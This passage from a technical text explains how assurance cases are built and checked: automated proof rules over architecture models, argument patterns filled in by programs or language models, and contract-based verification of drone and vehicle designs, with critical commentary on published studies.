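The search stops at Decrypt and never reaches c1, although anybody could tamper with a radio signal on its way to the aircraft. Decrypt's ability to reject forged messages is a separate claim. That claim has nothing beneath it in the part of the tree that Gacek and colleagues print, so its support has to come from elsewhere.

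Suppose an engineer adds connection c7, which delivers data unaltered from the handset receiver to Navigation, so that a person can take over by hand. Steps 1 and 2 stay the same, but step 3 must now cover c7 too. Since c7 doesn't come from Decrypt, Resolute must prove clean(Handset receiver). The only connection into the receiver is c6, a radio link that a stranger could alter, so clean_link(c6) fails. No other rule can make up for this failure, so the claims about the receiver, c7, Navigation, c5 and the motor controller fail in turn.

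The rules are the same in both versions. Engineers can also use the failed tree to find the bypass, because Resolute marks each failed claim and links it to the component or rule involved.

A bypass like this may be deliberate. Rockwell Collins report that a hobby radio controller communicated directly with their quadcopter's flight computer, as an independent means of control for safety during demonstration flights. When the proof fails because of such a link, engineers have to choose whether to remove it, protect it or settle for a weaker claim that makes an exception for it.

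The proof can also succeed only because the model is incomplete. Suppose the modeller includes c7 but leaves out the handset and c6, reasoning that a hand-held controller isn't part of the aircraft. The model then has no connections into the receiver, so any statement about every connection into it is automatically true. The receiver counts as clean and the proof succeeds, even though a stranger with a handset can still fly the aircraft.

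Even with the handset in the model, the proof correctly fails only because of one table entry, where the modeller recorded that c6 can be altered. The handset counts as clean because nothing leads into it. The shared-memory rule has a similar gap, because it succeeds without checking anything if the model doesn't place a process in any memory.

### From the small model to the real aircraft

Gacek and colleagues first wrote their rules for a simplified model, which let them test the requirements against a design before development began. The full model, with its 35 threads, had seven times as many software components, but they had to change very few rules. The rules refer to kinds of elements, such as connections and threads, so they mostly just apply more often in a larger model.

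The biggest change dealt with loops in the data flow. Suppose Navigation in the small model also reports the aircraft's position back to Command, through a new connection c8. To prove clean(Navigation), Resolute must prove clean(Command), and to prove that, it must prove clean(Navigation) again. Under the original rules, Resolute would repeat this loop forever. Accepting the repeated claim as already proved would make the claim support itself, which GSN forbids.

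Gacek and colleagues replaced these rules with ones that compute the set of components that messages can reach before passing through Decrypt. The argument then has to show that the set is complete and that no component in it has access to the motor controller.

In the small model without the bypass, outside messages can start at the ground radio or the handset. Messages from the ground radio go straight to Decrypt, where the calculation stops, and messages from the handset can reach only the receiver. The set contains the ground radio, the handset and the receiver, none of which can send anything to the motor controller except through Decrypt. If an engineer adds c7, messages from the handset can also reach Navigation, and from there the motor controller, so the claim fails. The calculation still finishes despite the loop through c8, because each component can join the set only once.

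The small number of rule changes is encouraging, but it comes from the tool's own developers working on one aircraft. They don't report how long the rules took to write or how the effort compares with drawing a case by hand. They say Resolute was useful for expressing requirements early in the design and checking later that those requirements still held. They also used it for claims about whether resources would be available in different operating modes.

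The 2014 version of Resolute had no place for GSN's context and assumptions, so an assumption such as "nobody can break the cipher without the key" would have to go in an accompanying document. Its rules can, however, combine subclaims with "or" as well as "and". The finished case no longer depends on Resolute or the model, so engineers can hand it to a certifier or export it to other assurance case tools.

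### Searching for known weaknesses

Engineers can also write rules for design mistakes that many systems share. *Towards an Automated Approach for Detecting Architectural Weaknesses in Critical Systems* (Santos, Suloglu and colleagues, 2020) describes a catalogue of 223 such weaknesses, grouped under 11 standard security measures. These differ from coding errors, which affect individual lines of a program. For example, a system might check a user's identity in the program on the user's own computer but not on the server. An attacker can remove that check from their copy of the program, however well the check is written.

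An engineer tags each relevant component with a role, such as "entry point" for a place where outside data comes in or "validator" for a component that checks it. The rules are reusable because they mention only these roles. Resolute doesn't allow negated claims, so each rule describes a property of a good design, for example that the system validates all its inputs. A failed proof then indicates a possible weakness.

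Santos and colleagues tried three rules on a model of a satellite's control software. In a later paper, Santos, Suloglu and colleagues, in *A Methodological Approach to Verify Architecture Resiliency*, applied three more to a model of a robot for exploring the Moon. All six claims failed:

| Model | Failed claim | Problem found |
|---|---|---|
| Satellite | The system validates its inputs | Nothing validates commands from the ground |
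| Satellite | The system authenticates whoever sends commands | Nothing checks the ground station's identity |
| Satellite | The system encrypts sensitive data before sending it | Nothing encrypts the data sent to the ground |
| Lunar robot | The system logs security-relevant operations | The data logger has no connection to the part that regulates the actuators |
| Lunar robot | The system detects failed components by their heartbeats | The cameras send a heartbeat every 20 seconds, but the receiver checks every 10 |
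| Lunar robot | Nobody reaches the controls without authorisation | The operator panel connects directly to the control system |

A heartbeat is a regular message that shows a component, such as a camera, is still working. If the receiver checks for heartbeats too often, it may treat a working camera as failed.

The findings depend on the tags as well as the design. The satellite's command-processing thread might validate commands somewhere in its code, but the claim would still fail if no component had the "validator" tag. A failed proof is therefore a reason to look more closely but doesn't establish that the weakness exists. Each paper is a demonstration on a single model, and neither counts false alarms or missed weaknesses.

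The heartbeat result is less clear than it looks. The robot's model gives the receiver an "acceptable silence" of 20, apparently also in seconds, which matches the interval between the cameras' messages. The printed part of the rule requires the sending and checking rates to be equal and does not use this figure. The cameras may therefore be a borderline case, and the rule would also reject a component that sent heartbeats more often than necessary.

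### Why people must review the rules

Resolute guarantees only that a conclusion follows from the rules and the model, as Gacek and colleagues acknowledge. A user could write a rule with the sentence "The aircraft is safe" and a condition that is always true, and the program would produce a successful assurance case. Resolute keeps a case consistent with the model, but the quality of the case depends on its users, and experts still have to review it.

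Reviewers should start by comparing each English sentence with the condition beneath it. According to the sentence in the worked example, the component "only receives messages that pass Decrypt", but the condition makes an exception for sensor data. That exception is reasonable because sensors don't encrypt their readings. But if the sensors include a GPS receiver, an attacker might steer the aircraft with fake GPS signals, and the claim would still be proved. Someone who read only the finished tree could easily miss this risk.

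Published rules also contain apparent small mistakes. The lunar robot's heartbeat rule is supposed to match each sender with a receiver, but as printed it takes the receiver from the list of senders.

One rule in a car security report from the Software Engineering Institute (2015) requires a receiving component's trust level to be at least as high as the sender's. This keeps secrets from going to less trusted components, but it doesn't stop those components from sending commands to more trusted ones. An entertainment system with low trust could send instructions to highly trusted brakes without breaking the rule, although the report describes attacks that reached a car's brakes from its entertainment system. The comment above the rule also states the comparison in the opposite direction from the code.

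A companion rule would catch that attack by requiring connected components to belong to the same group, such as cruise control. But both rules check only components that have the relevant label, so if an engineer forgets to label the entertainment system, both pass without checking it.

The institute's engineers checked their rules by hand, particularly when one failed. But a faulty rule that passes is more dangerous than one that fails, because nobody has a reason to investigate it. Resolute may apply one rule in dozens of places, so a single mistake can weaken many branches of a case, but reviewers can concentrate on a short list of rules instead of reading every branch.

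Hardin (2025) presents Resolint, a companion tool to Resolute that can help with missing information. It checks whether a model follows modelling guidelines, which engineers also write as Resolute rules. A guideline requiring every process to have a memory, or every component to have a group, would close some of the gaps described above. Resolute later became part of BriefCASE, a larger toolset that Cofer (2022) describes as combining design, verification and code generation.

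Reviewers can also test a rule by deliberately putting a fault in the model. Engineers at the Software Engineering Institute moved a wheel sensor out of the cruise control group and confirmed that the group rule then failed. For the quadcopter, a reviewer could add c7 to the model with and without the handset. The reviewer would see that the rules catch the bypass only when the handset is included, before anybody relied on the proof.

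## Filling in argument patterns by program and by language model

Resolute's proof search suits claims that follow from how a system's parts connect. Most assurance cases must also combine hazards, test reports and expert judgement, and engineers often do this by adapting an argument that worked for an earlier system. An argument pattern is a reusable argument with blanks for the details of a particular system. Filling in the blanks is slow and repetitive, but ordinary programs can do much of it when the details are already in machine-readable models. More recently, researchers have tried language models for systems described only in written documents.

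### Roles, multiplicities and choices

Engineers call the blanks in a pattern roles and write them in curly brackets, as in {hazard}. A multiplicity marks a part of the argument that they must repeat, for example once for every hazard. A choice offers different ways to support the same claim. The small pattern below is an illustration with all three, but its two kinds of support, showing that a hazard can't happen or that it is rare enough, come from the GSN standard's sample argument.

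- Goal G1: {System} is acceptably safe.
  - Context C1: {Hazard list}
  - Strategy S1: Argument over every hazard on the list
    - Goal G2 (one for each hazard): The design deals adequately with {hazard}.
      - Choose one:
        - Goal G3: The design rules out {hazard}.
          - Solution Sn1: {Analysis of the design}
        - Goal G4: The yearly probability of {hazard} is below {limit}.
          - Solution Sn2: {Fault tree}

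Suppose the quadcopter's analysts have listed three hazards:

| Hazard | Chosen goal | Evidence so far |
|---|---|---|
| Obeying a stranger | G3 | Trace of every connection in the architecture model |
| Flying too close to a person | G4, limit 1 in 100,000 | None |
| Flying with too little charge to land | G4, limit 1 in 10,000 | Fault tree for the battery |

Filling in the pattern by hand gives this argument:

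- Goal G1: The quadcopter is acceptably safe.
  - Context C1: Hazard list, version 3
  - Strategy S1: Argument over every hazard on the list
    - Goal G2.1: The design deals adequately with "obeying a stranger".
      - Goal G3.1: The design rules out "obeying a stranger".
        - Solution Sn1.1: Trace of every connection
    - Goal G2.2: The design deals adequately with "flying too close to a person".
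      - Goal G4.2: The yearly probability of "flying too close to a person" is below 1 in 100,000. *(undeveloped)*
    - Goal G2.3: The design deals adequately with "flying with too little charge to land".
      - Goal G4.3: The yearly probability of "flying with too little charge to land" is below 1 in 10,000.
        - Solution Sn2.3: Fault tree for the battery

GSN marks a goal as undeveloped when nothing supports it yet, so the missing evidence for G4.2 is easy to see. With 50 hazards and complete evidence, the same pattern would produce 153 elements, and somebody would have to update them whenever the hazard list changed.

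The tree also contains a mistake that is much harder to see. The trace doesn't show that Decrypt rejects forged messages, so Sn1.1 supports only part of G3.1. The argument still follows the pattern correctly, because filling in a blank puts evidence under a claim without checking that the evidence is good enough, whoever or whatever fills it in.

### Linking a pattern to design models

*Weaving an Assurance Case from Design* (Hawkins, Habli and colleagues, 2015) replaces the hand-made table with the design models. Its program takes the pattern, the models and a weaving model, which records where to find the value for each role. For example, the weaving model might link the role {trusted software component} to a particular kind of element in AADL.

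Their example is an encryption controller that sits between a private network and a public one. Each message from the private side has a header, which contains the destination, and some content. A component called crypto encrypts the content, and another, called bypass, passes on the header unencrypted because the public network has to read it to deliver the message. The policy is that no unencrypted content may reach the public network. Enforcing it depends on crypto and bypass working correctly, but the components that handle traffic on either side can be completely untrusted.

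The pattern splits the policy into a claim about each trusted component and a claim about how the components fit together. The program then works as follows:

1. It searches the pattern for blanks and repeated parts, and finds that it needs one goal for each trusted software component.
2. It looks up this role in the weaving model to learn what kind of element to search for.
3. It reads the matching elements, crypto and bypass, from the AADL model.
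4. It writes out the goals "crypto enforces its local policy" and "bypass enforces its local policy", with the links that connect them to the rest of the argument.

The weaving model refers to kinds of elements rather than individual components, so if the designers add another trusted component, the next run produces another goal without any edits to the weaving model.

An architecture model rarely contains everything a case needs. Hawkins, Habli and Kelly point out in *The Need for a Weaving Model in Assurance Case Automation* that a case also has to justify confidence in its own evidence. If a formal proof supports a claim, the case should explain why the proof technique and tools are trustworthy. That information doesn't belong in an AADL model, so they took it from separate models of the verification process. The weaving model also has to link these sources to one another. For example,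 a failure mode in an FMEA should correspond to an error type in the architecture model. If a source isn't available in a form the program can read, the role stays blank for a person to fill in.

Hawkins and colleagues say that one benefit of automation is that it eliminates human error in filling in patterns, but they also say that a correct weaving model is crucial. Automation therefore mostly moves the errors into the weaving model. If an engineer links {trusted software component} to the wrong kind of element, the program will leave out some components every time it runs, and the finished argument will still look complete.

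People also still write the patterns, which Hawkins and colleagues regard as creative work that will remain largely manual. Their evaluation shows only that the approach is feasible, but the problem they want to solve is real. They describe many arguments used in practice as "cartoon arguments" that are too abstract, much as Gleirscher and Carlan observed.

### Claims from a hazard spreadsheet

Hazard analysts often keep their results in a spreadsheet, which the weaving approach can't use until someone converts it into a structured model. Yan, Foster and colleagues (2022) automate this conversion in *Model-Based Generation of Hazard-Driven Arguments and Formal Verification Evidence for Assurance Cases*. Each row of their table can contain a hazard, a cause, a safety requirement, and the methods and results of checking that requirement. The program creates a claim for each hazard, puts claims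 about its causes beneath it, and continues down to the evidence. Like the script that turns STPA results into a tree, this part of the program only arranges what analysts have entered.

The program can also query the design to create claims that nobody has typed in. Yan and colleagues demonstrate this on an underwater maintenance robot. A safety monitor switches the robot between four modes: normal automatic operation, high caution, collision avoidance and operator control. One requirement is that the operator can take control from any mode in which they don't already have it.

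The program lists the three other modes from a state machine, a diagram of the modes and the transitions between them. It creates one claim for each mode, such as that the operator's request triggers a transition from the high-caution mode to operator control. It then searches for these transitions, finds all three, and cites them as evidence. If a designer later adds a fifth mode, the next run will create a fourth claim, which will have no evidence until the new mode has such a transition.

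The wording of the query matters because a claim that a transition exists with a certain trigger and destination is also true if the transition has an extra condition, such as working only below a certain speed. The operator could then request control and not get it. A reviewer would have to notice that the query doesn't exclude such conditions.

When searching the diagram isn't enough to check a claim, the program writes an assertion for a model checker, a tool that explores a model's possible behaviours. In the example, the assertion is that the robot can reach operator control. Engineers can avoid writing formal logic if they use fixed phrases in the spreadsheet, which let the program recognise what to check. In the 2022 version, a person still had to run the model checker. People also supply the hazards, causes, pattern and query rules. Yan and colleagues say that queries don't suit every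 type of claim.

### Arguments from component contracts

A manufacturer may use the same component in many vehicles and need a slightly different argument for each. Sljivo, Gallina and colleagues generate these arguments from contracts in *Generation of Safety Case Argument-Fragments from Safety Contracts*. Each contract states what a component assumes about its inputs and what it guarantees about its outputs if those assumptions hold. Strong contracts must hold wherever the component is used, while weak contracts apply only in settings that satisfy their assumptions.

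Their example comes from Scania trucks and buses. If the fuel gauge shows more fuel than the tank contains, the engine may stop without warning on a motorway. The component that estimates the fuel level must therefore be accurate to within 5%. In simplified form, the relevant contracts are:

| Component | Assumes | Guarantees |
|---|---|---|
| Engine management system | Engine status is less than 0.3 seconds old | Fuel consumption figure is within 1% of the true value (in fact 0.4%) |
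| Fuel estimator | Consumption figure is within 1% of the true value, and the tank size is in a set range | Estimated fuel level is within 1% of the true value |

The estimator's guarantee of 1% is stricter than the required 5%, and the engine system's 0.4% satisfies the estimator's assumption. The generated argument follows this chain, with a goal for the requirement, a goal beneath it for the estimator's contract, and a pointer to the part of the case that covers the engine system's contract. It also has goals stating that the strong contracts hold and that the contracts don't contradict each other. Where evidence is missing, the rules produce an undeveloped goal.

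Engineers write the contracts, record which contracts support which requirements, and attach evidence such as simulation reports. The generation rules follow the recorded links, so people or contract-verification tools have to check separately that the numbers are consistent.

In the published example, the engine system's strong contract allows consumption figures from −1 to 3,212, but the estimator's accuracy contract assumes figures from 0 to 3,212. The −1 is presumably an error code. If the engine system sent it, the estimator's guarantee would apply only if the separate fuel-level sensor met its own conditions. Sljivo and colleagues had worked through this example when they published the rules, and planned to build the rules into a tool later.

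### One case for a family of products

A product with *n* optional features can have up to 2*ⁿ* versions, too many to write a separate case for each when *n* is large. In *Assurance Case Development for Evolving Software Product Lines*, Murphy, Viger and colleagues (2025) build a single case for the whole family and label each part with the versions it applies to.

They demonstrate the method on infusion pumps with 20 valid combinations of features. The main claim is that a pump stops giving the drug immediately after an alarm. A query lists every alarm state in the model and the features a pump needs to enter it. For example, only pumps that monitor the infusion rate have an alarm for exceeding the hard limit on that rate. The program creates a goal for this alarm, labeled "pumps that monitor the infusion rate". A model checker designed for product families then checks all those pumps together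 and finds no violation.

Murphy and colleagues next changed the family. They gave pumps with a display a history of past infusions, and added a feature that lets users program an infusion. The number of valid combinations grew to 25. The tool went through the old case and worked out how much of it still applied. For the model-checking result on the infusion-rate alarm, it gave these answers:

| Version of the pump | Mark | Reason |
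|---|---|---|
| Existing version without a display | Reuse | Nothing relevant has changed |
| Existing version with a display | Recheck | The new history screens might affect the result |
| New version with programmable infusion | Revise | The old evidence doesn't cover it |

The tool also found that programmable infusion introduces a new alarm for an unsafe rate, which needs its own branch of the argument. The manufacturer could release the update for pumps without a display while engineers repeated the check for those with one.

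Murphy and colleagues prove that their method gives the same answer for each version as a separate analysis of that version would. This guarantee is stronger than those of the other generators in this section, but it covers the method, not the content of the case. Engineers have to verify the argument templates by hand beforehand, label the features in the model, and translate each claim into logic. The published formula requires that the pump not enter its normal infusion state right after the alarm, so somebody has to confirm that the pump doesn't deliver the drug in any other state. The generated case includes an explicit goal for justifying the translation. The case covers only part of the pump's safety, and Murphy and colleagues designed it to demonstrate the method.

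### Asking a language model to fill in the pattern

All of these programs need structured inputs, but many developers have only design documents and test reports written in prose, which language models can read. *Automatic Instantiation of Assurance Cases from Patterns Using Large Language Models* (Odu, Belle and colleagues, 2024) tests how well GPT-4o and GPT-4 Turbo can turn a pattern into a finished case.

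They first rewrote each GSN pattern as a list of short statements. For example, `HasMultiplicity(S1, G3, 1 of *)` means that strategy S1 needs one or more copies of goal G3. Depending on the set-up, the prompt also contained a worked example, a guide to GSN, or information about the system. The model output an assurance case as structured text, which a person could redraw as a diagram.

The test material came from published papers that included a pattern and a case people had derived from it. It covered a collision avoidance system for drones, an underwater vehicle, an infusion pump, an instant messaging server and a DeepMind system for diagnosing eye disease. There were nine set-ups, and those with a worked example used the eye-disease case. Each model ran five times on each system.

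Odu and colleagues scored the output's similarity to the human-written case in three ways. The first score measures how closely the characters match, and the second, BLEU, counts shared sequences of words. The third, semantic similarity, compares the texts as vectors and equals 1 for identical texts. The table shows GPT-4o's median semantic similarity in three of the set-ups.

| System | No pattern or other help | Pattern and rules for reading it | Pattern, rules, GSN guide and system information |
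|---|---|---|---|
| Drone collision avoidance | 0.23 | 0.85 | 0.92 |
| Underwater vehicle | 0.08 | 0.59 | 0.90 |
| Infusion pump | 0.04 | 0.27 | 0.76 |
| Messaging server | 0.09 | 0.54 | 0.70 |

The high scores in the last column are best read alongside those in the middle column. For the drone system, GPT-4o scored 0.85 when the prompt contained the pattern but no information about the system beyond its name. Its character-matching score was 0.82 without the system information and 0.85 with it. Much of a finished case is wording copied from its pattern, so a model can score well while getting the important details wrong. The infusion pump is a better test because the score there depended much more on the extra information. But Odu and colleagues took that information from the same papers that contained the human-written cases.

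The models were also unreliable at choosing how often to repeat parts of a pattern. In one set-up for the underwater vehicle, GPT-4o produced 42 elements and GPT-4 Turbo produced 18, while the human-written case had 24. The pattern called for "one or more" copies of a certain goal, and the human-written case included three, but GPT-4 Turbo wrote only one. GPT-4o wrote all three and also developed two that the human-written case had left undeveloped, which may explain its higher total.

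A longer case isn't necessarily worse, but a missing branch can leave a hazard out of the argument entirely. An ordinary program avoids this by counting the entries in a model or table. Engineers could therefore ask a language model only to extract the entries and cite the source document for each, then have a program build the tree. Odu and colleagues recommend a semi-automatic approach because the models' results fell short of the experts'.

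### The Baidu Apollo study

In *LLM-Based Safety Case Generation for Baidu Apollo*, Odu, Belle and Wang applied the same approach to open-source software for self-driving cars. They focused on the component that predicts where other road users will go, which uses several learned models. They first wrote a safety case by hand, following three of the six stages of AMLAS, a published method for assuring machine-learning components. The safety case had 38 elements, including 15 goals and five pieces of evidence.

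GPT-4o then tried to recreate the case, five times with supporting knowledge and five times without. Its average semantic similarity to the hand-written case was 0.82 with the knowledge and 0.21 without, while BLEU fell from 0.47 to 0.01.

However, the supporting knowledge included material that Odu and colleagues had produced while writing the case by hand, such as the safety requirements. Because GPT-4o was given many of the answers, the experiment mainly measures how well it can arrange finished analysis into GSN. That skill is useful, but the analysis is harder, and Odu and colleagues report that gathering the material took considerable expertise in several fields.

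Similarity to the hand-written case is also a doubtful measure of quality here. The team worked from public sources and had no access to real driving data, so they assumed the component had shown no erroneous behaviour. They also required its average error in predicting positions to stay within 0.001 metres. No system is likely to predict a pedestrian's movements to within a millimetre, but a model that copied this figure would score higher than one that flagged it as unrealistic.

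### Language models as reviewers

Reviewing a case requires different skills from writing one. In *LLMs as Judges*, Yu, Sivakumar and colleagues (2025) asked GPT-4o, GPT-4.1, DeepSeek-R1 and Gemini 2.0 Flash to review four human-written cases, including the one for Baidu Apollo. The models applied four criteria from the GSN standard: whether a reader can follow the argument, whether its structure is valid, whether it is expressed clearly and completely, and whether it stands up to criticism. The researchers used three prompt styles and ran each combination of model, case, criterion and prompt style five times, producing 960 reviews.

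Each review included a mark from 1, for a perfect case, to 5. The models gave similar marks on average, all between 2.5 and 3.75, but disagreed about which cases deserved them. Yu and colleagues measured agreement with Fleiss' kappa, which is 1 when reviewers always agree and about 0 when they agree no more often than they would by chance. The values ranged from −0.16 to 0.15, so a developer shouldn't give much weight to any single mark.

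The comments were more useful than the marks. One human assessor rated how informative each of the 960 reviews was, again with 1 as the best score. Average ratings were between 2.65 and 3.65 for short prompts, and between 1.1 and 2.05 when the prompt told the model to identify each issue, explain it and suggest a remedy. In one good example, DeepSeek-R1 pointed out that nothing supported the claim that an infusion pump prevents overdoses, and listed tests that could provide evidence.

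An ordinary program can find every unsupported goal too. The models were less dependable at this kind of work, sometimes referring to elements that weren't in the case or missing some of the elements with duplicate labels. It makes sense to run a structural checker first and use the language model for questions that need an understanding of the text, such as what might defeat an argument.

Yu and colleagues didn't calculate what proportion of real flaws the models found, because no agreed list of flaws exists for these cases. But they did know that the infusion pump and messaging cases both had duplicate labels, and that some of the messaging server's goals had no support. Counting how often each model reported these flaws would have given a small but objective test. A stronger test would add faults to a sound case and count how many each reviewer finds.

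### Comparing the structure of human and machine cases

Text similarity does not measure how the parts of an argument connect. *Evaluating Assurance Cases as Text-Attributed Graphs for Structure and Provenance Analysis* (Ikhwantri and Marijan, 2026) treats each assurance case as a graph, with claims and evidence as nodes and the links between them as edges. The collection contains 46 human-written cases and 217 written by GPT-4o, including cases from the 2024 study by Odu and colleagues.

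To compare a machine-written case with the human original, they pair up nodes with similar text and then check whether the same pairs are linked in both. The results differed between two sets of cases:

| Source of the cases | Share of human nodes with a partner | Score for matching links (F1) |
|---|---|---|
| Odu and colleagues | 0.75 | 0.50 |
| An earlier study by Sivakumar and colleagues | 0.99 | 0.18 |

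F1 combines the share of the machine's links that are correct with the share of the human links that the machine reproduced, and a perfect score is 1. Ikhwantri and Marijan conclude that GPT-4o captures content more reliably than structure.

The figures don't fully support this conclusion, because the published formula sets no minimum similarity for two nodes to become partners. Matching can therefore continue until one case runs out of nodes, and the first column would then depend mostly on length. The averages fit this explanation. In the Sivakumar set, the machine-written cases had about 16 nodes and the human ones 11.5, while in the Odu set they had 17 and 24. A high share of nodes with partners therefore doesn't show that GPT-4o recovered the content.

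The link scores may also reflect some structural errors that did not come from the original generation. The original datasets contained only the text of the machine-written nodes, so Ikhwantri and Marijan asked GPT-4o to add the links afterwards.

They also trained graph neural networks, which learn from nodes and their connections, to tell human-written cases from machine-written ones. The networks did this well, with an F1 of about 0.94. A regulator could use such a tool to select cases for closer inspection, but it can't show whether an argument is sound. The networks may also rely on superficial differences, since 39 of the 46 human-written cases in the collection come from a single drone dataset with its own format.

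### The NASA survey and newer models

In a survey for NASA, Graydon and Lehman (2025) examined 14 works that propose using language models on assurance arguments. Only eight included a study of how well the proposal worked. The survey raised objections about training data, toy examples and the need for human supervision. According to Yu and colleagues, it concluded that a definitive answer would need further research. The studies above give some idea of how serious each objection is.

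A model's training data may include the case that it is supposed to write. GPT-4o's training data runs to October 2023, and the human-written cases for the infusion pump, the messaging server and the underwater vehicle appeared between 2017 and 2021. GPT-4o scored very low when it had only the system's name, so it probably couldn't reproduce these cases unprompted. But a pattern contains much of a case's wording and could help a model reproduce the rest. Researchers could avoid this problem by testing on unpublished cases.

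The examples are small. The four cases in the main test by Odu and colleagues had between 24 and 27 elements, and the largest case Yu and colleagues used had 76. Both papers mention an air traffic control safety case that is more than 500 pages long and refers to about 400 documents. A model that can organise a few pages of relevant facts may still struggle to find the right sentence among hundreds of documents, or to notice that two of them contradict each other.

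Supervision is harder to assess. When a program fills in a pattern, reviewers can concentrate on the pattern and the links to the models, as they can on Resolute's rules. A language model can make a mistake anywhere in the text, and the mistake may be as fluent as the rest, so a reviewer has to check every claim against its source. Language models save effort only if this checking takes less time than writing the case. An experiment could test this by timing engineers on both tasks, which similarity scores don't measure.

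The scores in these studies are a poor guide to what current models can do. The newest models tested date from 2025, and even Ikhwantri and Marijan, writing in 2026, analysed the output of GPT-4o. Current models can work for much longer and handle far more material, so they would probably follow a pattern's instructions more accurately and invent fewer elements. Better models won't fix the tests, though, because a case that copies the pattern's wording would still score highly even if it cited the wrong fault tree.

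## Proving properties of the design and carrying them into the built system

Some of the evidence for claims about how a system behaves can come from proofs about its design. A trace of connections shows that commands reach the quadcopter's motors only through Decrypt, but not that the speeds in those commands stay within limits. That depends on what each component does with its inputs. Engineers also need evidence for each step from the design model to the running program.

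### Checking that contracts fit together

The generator that Sljivo and colleagues built for truck software followed the links between components' contracts, with their paired assumptions and guarantees, but left people or other tools to check the numbers. AGREE, a tool for AADL models, does that checking. Cofer, Amundson and colleagues (2022), in *Cyber Assured Systems Engineering at Scale*, describe its two main checks:

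- **Interfaces:** each component's guarantees must satisfy the assumptions of the components that receive its outputs.
- **Whole system:** the system's own assumptions, together with the guarantees of its parts, must imply the system's guarantees.

In a small example, a number enters the system and passes through component A, then component B. The contracts for A and B come from Cofer (2022), in *Cyber Assured Systems Engineering*, but the system's guarantee is added here for illustration.

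| | Assumes | Guarantees |
|---|---|---|
| Whole system | Input below 10 | Output below 35 |
| A | Input below 20 | Output less than twice its input |
| B | Input below 20 | Output less than its input plus 15 |

The system's input is below 10, so A's assumption holds. A's output is then below 20, which is what B assumes. B's output is therefore below 20 + 15 = 35, and both checks pass without anyone having to look inside A or B.

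Suppose an engineer replaces A with a version that guarantees only an output less than three times its input. An input of 9 could then produce 26, but B assumes an input below 20, so the interface check fails. B might still work correctly with 26, but its contract doesn't cover that input, so the engineer can't use the contracts to conclude anything about the system's output. The engineer can tighten A's guarantee, limit the system's input to 6, or show that B works over a wider range.

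Whether a set of contracts proves a system's guarantee can depend on the data type. Cofer's full example has a third component, C, which adds its two inputs, and the system guarantees an output below 50. Suppose C's inputs are the outputs of A and B. If all the values are whole numbers, the system's input is at most 9, A's output at most 17 and B's at most 31, so the total is at most 48 and the guarantee holds. If the values can be decimals, an input of 9.9 allows 19.7 from A and 34.6 from B, which add up to 54.3 and break the guarantee.

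Working with contracts also saves effort. Heiser (2026) reports in *seL4* that the effort of verifying software grows with the square of the size of its specification. Splitting a specification into ten equal parts could in theory cut the work to a tenth, though Heiser calls this highly optimistic because the parts usually add up to more than the original.

A contract can also be true but too weak to use. *Function Contracts and Beyond* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a small C library for lists of numbers. Its counting function requires the list to be short enough for the count to fit in an ordinary integer. In the initial contracts, the functions for adding and removing entries guaranteed only that some list would exist afterwards. Each function provably met its contract. But a program that added two entries, removed one and then counted the rest could not be proved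 safe, because the contracts left the length of the list unknown. The remedy was to strengthen the contracts to guarantee exactly which list results from each call, without changing the code.

### How a model checker proves something about every run

The example with A and B follows one number through the system once. Real components run repeatedly and keep state between steps, so AGREE has to prove that a guarantee holds at every step of a run of any length. The Alloy search for the calendar agent, by contrast, only covered runs up to a fixed number of steps.

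AGREE uses a form of mathematical induction. In ordinary induction, the tool shows that the system starts in a good state and that every good state leads only to another good state, so the system can never reach a bad one.

Induction can fail to prove a property even when the property is true. For example, a timer starts at 0 and adds 1 at each step, except that it goes from 3 back to 0. The claim is that it never reads 5. This holds at the start, but the induction fails because a timer reading 4 satisfies the claim and would read 5 next. The timer never reads 4 either, but the tool hasn't established that.

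*k*-induction solves this by looking at *k* states in a row. With *k* = 2, the tool checks that the first two states are good and that any two good states in a row are followed by another good state. For the timer to read 5, it must have read 4 just before and 3 before that. But a timer at 3 goes to 0, so no such sequence exists and the proof succeeds.

AGREE translates the model and its contracts into the language Lustre. It then looks for a violation using an SMT solver, a program that searches for values satisfying a set of logical conditions. If the solver finds a violation that begins at the system's real starting state, the design or a contract is wrong, and the engineer can replay the steps. If it finds one only in the induction step, as with the timer at 4, the tool can try a larger *k*, or the engineer can supply a fact such as "the timer never exceeds 3". A fact that is true in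 every reachable state and preserved by each step is called an inductive invariant. *Compositional Inductive Invariant Inference via Assume-Guarantee Reasoning* (2025) gives rules for combining contracts with each component's invariants, so that invariants can also be found one component at a time.

### BriefCASE, from the model to the binary

An AGREE proof depends on each component satisfying its contract and on components affecting one another only through the connections in the model. BriefCASE, the toolset that also contains Resolute, produces evidence for both conditions.

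Cofer and colleagues demonstrate this approach on a surveillance drone. The drone's mission computer originally ran four programs: a radio, a flight planner, a waypoint manager that divides the flight plan into segments, and a serial link to the flight controller. The flight planner was existing Linux software that the team wanted to keep unmodified.

Two analysis tools examined the AADL model for weaknesses and identified the ground station and the planner as the main sources of attack. This led to seven new requirements covering trust in the ground station, message integrity and misbehaviour while the system runs. Each requirement that engineers accept enters the assurance case as an undeveloped goal. They can reject a suggested requirement, but they have to record why.

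The engineers then chose remedies from a library of automatic changes to the model. BriefCASE inserted the new components, connected them and updated the case:

| Addition | Purpose |
|---|---|
| Attestation manager and gate | Check the ground station's software, and block messages from stations that fail |
| Three filters after the radio | Pass only well-formed messages |
| One filter after the planner | Pass only well-formed flight plans |
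| Geofence monitor | Raise an alert if a plan enters a forbidden zone or leaves a permitted one |
| Response monitor | Raise an alert if the planner stops responding |
| Virtual machine | Confine the planner and its copy of Linux |

AGREE checked the contracts of the enlarged design, including whether the geofence monitor's guarantees satisfy the waypoint manager's assumptions. The processor gives each program a fixed time slot, so BriefCASE included this schedule in the contracts before the check. A separate tool, Awas, traces information through the model and can confirm that everything from the ground station passes through the gate and filters before reaching the flight controller.

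A tool called SPLAT generates the code for the filters and monitors from their contracts and proves that the two match. The code is in a language called CakeML, whose compiler has also been proved correct, so the guarantee extends to the binary that the processor executes. CakeML programs occasionally pause to reclaim memory, which makes their timing less predictable. Cofer and colleagues had not found this to be a problem, but they advise considering it where timing is strict.

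The attestation manager has no AGREE contract and comes from a library that the developers verified separately. It sends the ground station a request containing a fresh number, so an attacker can't replay an old answer. A program on the ground station measures the control software and returns signed results. That program runs on Linux and could be compromised, so a second program, outside the Linux virtual machine, measures both Linux and the first program. If the results are acceptable, the aircraft adds the station to its list of trusted computers.

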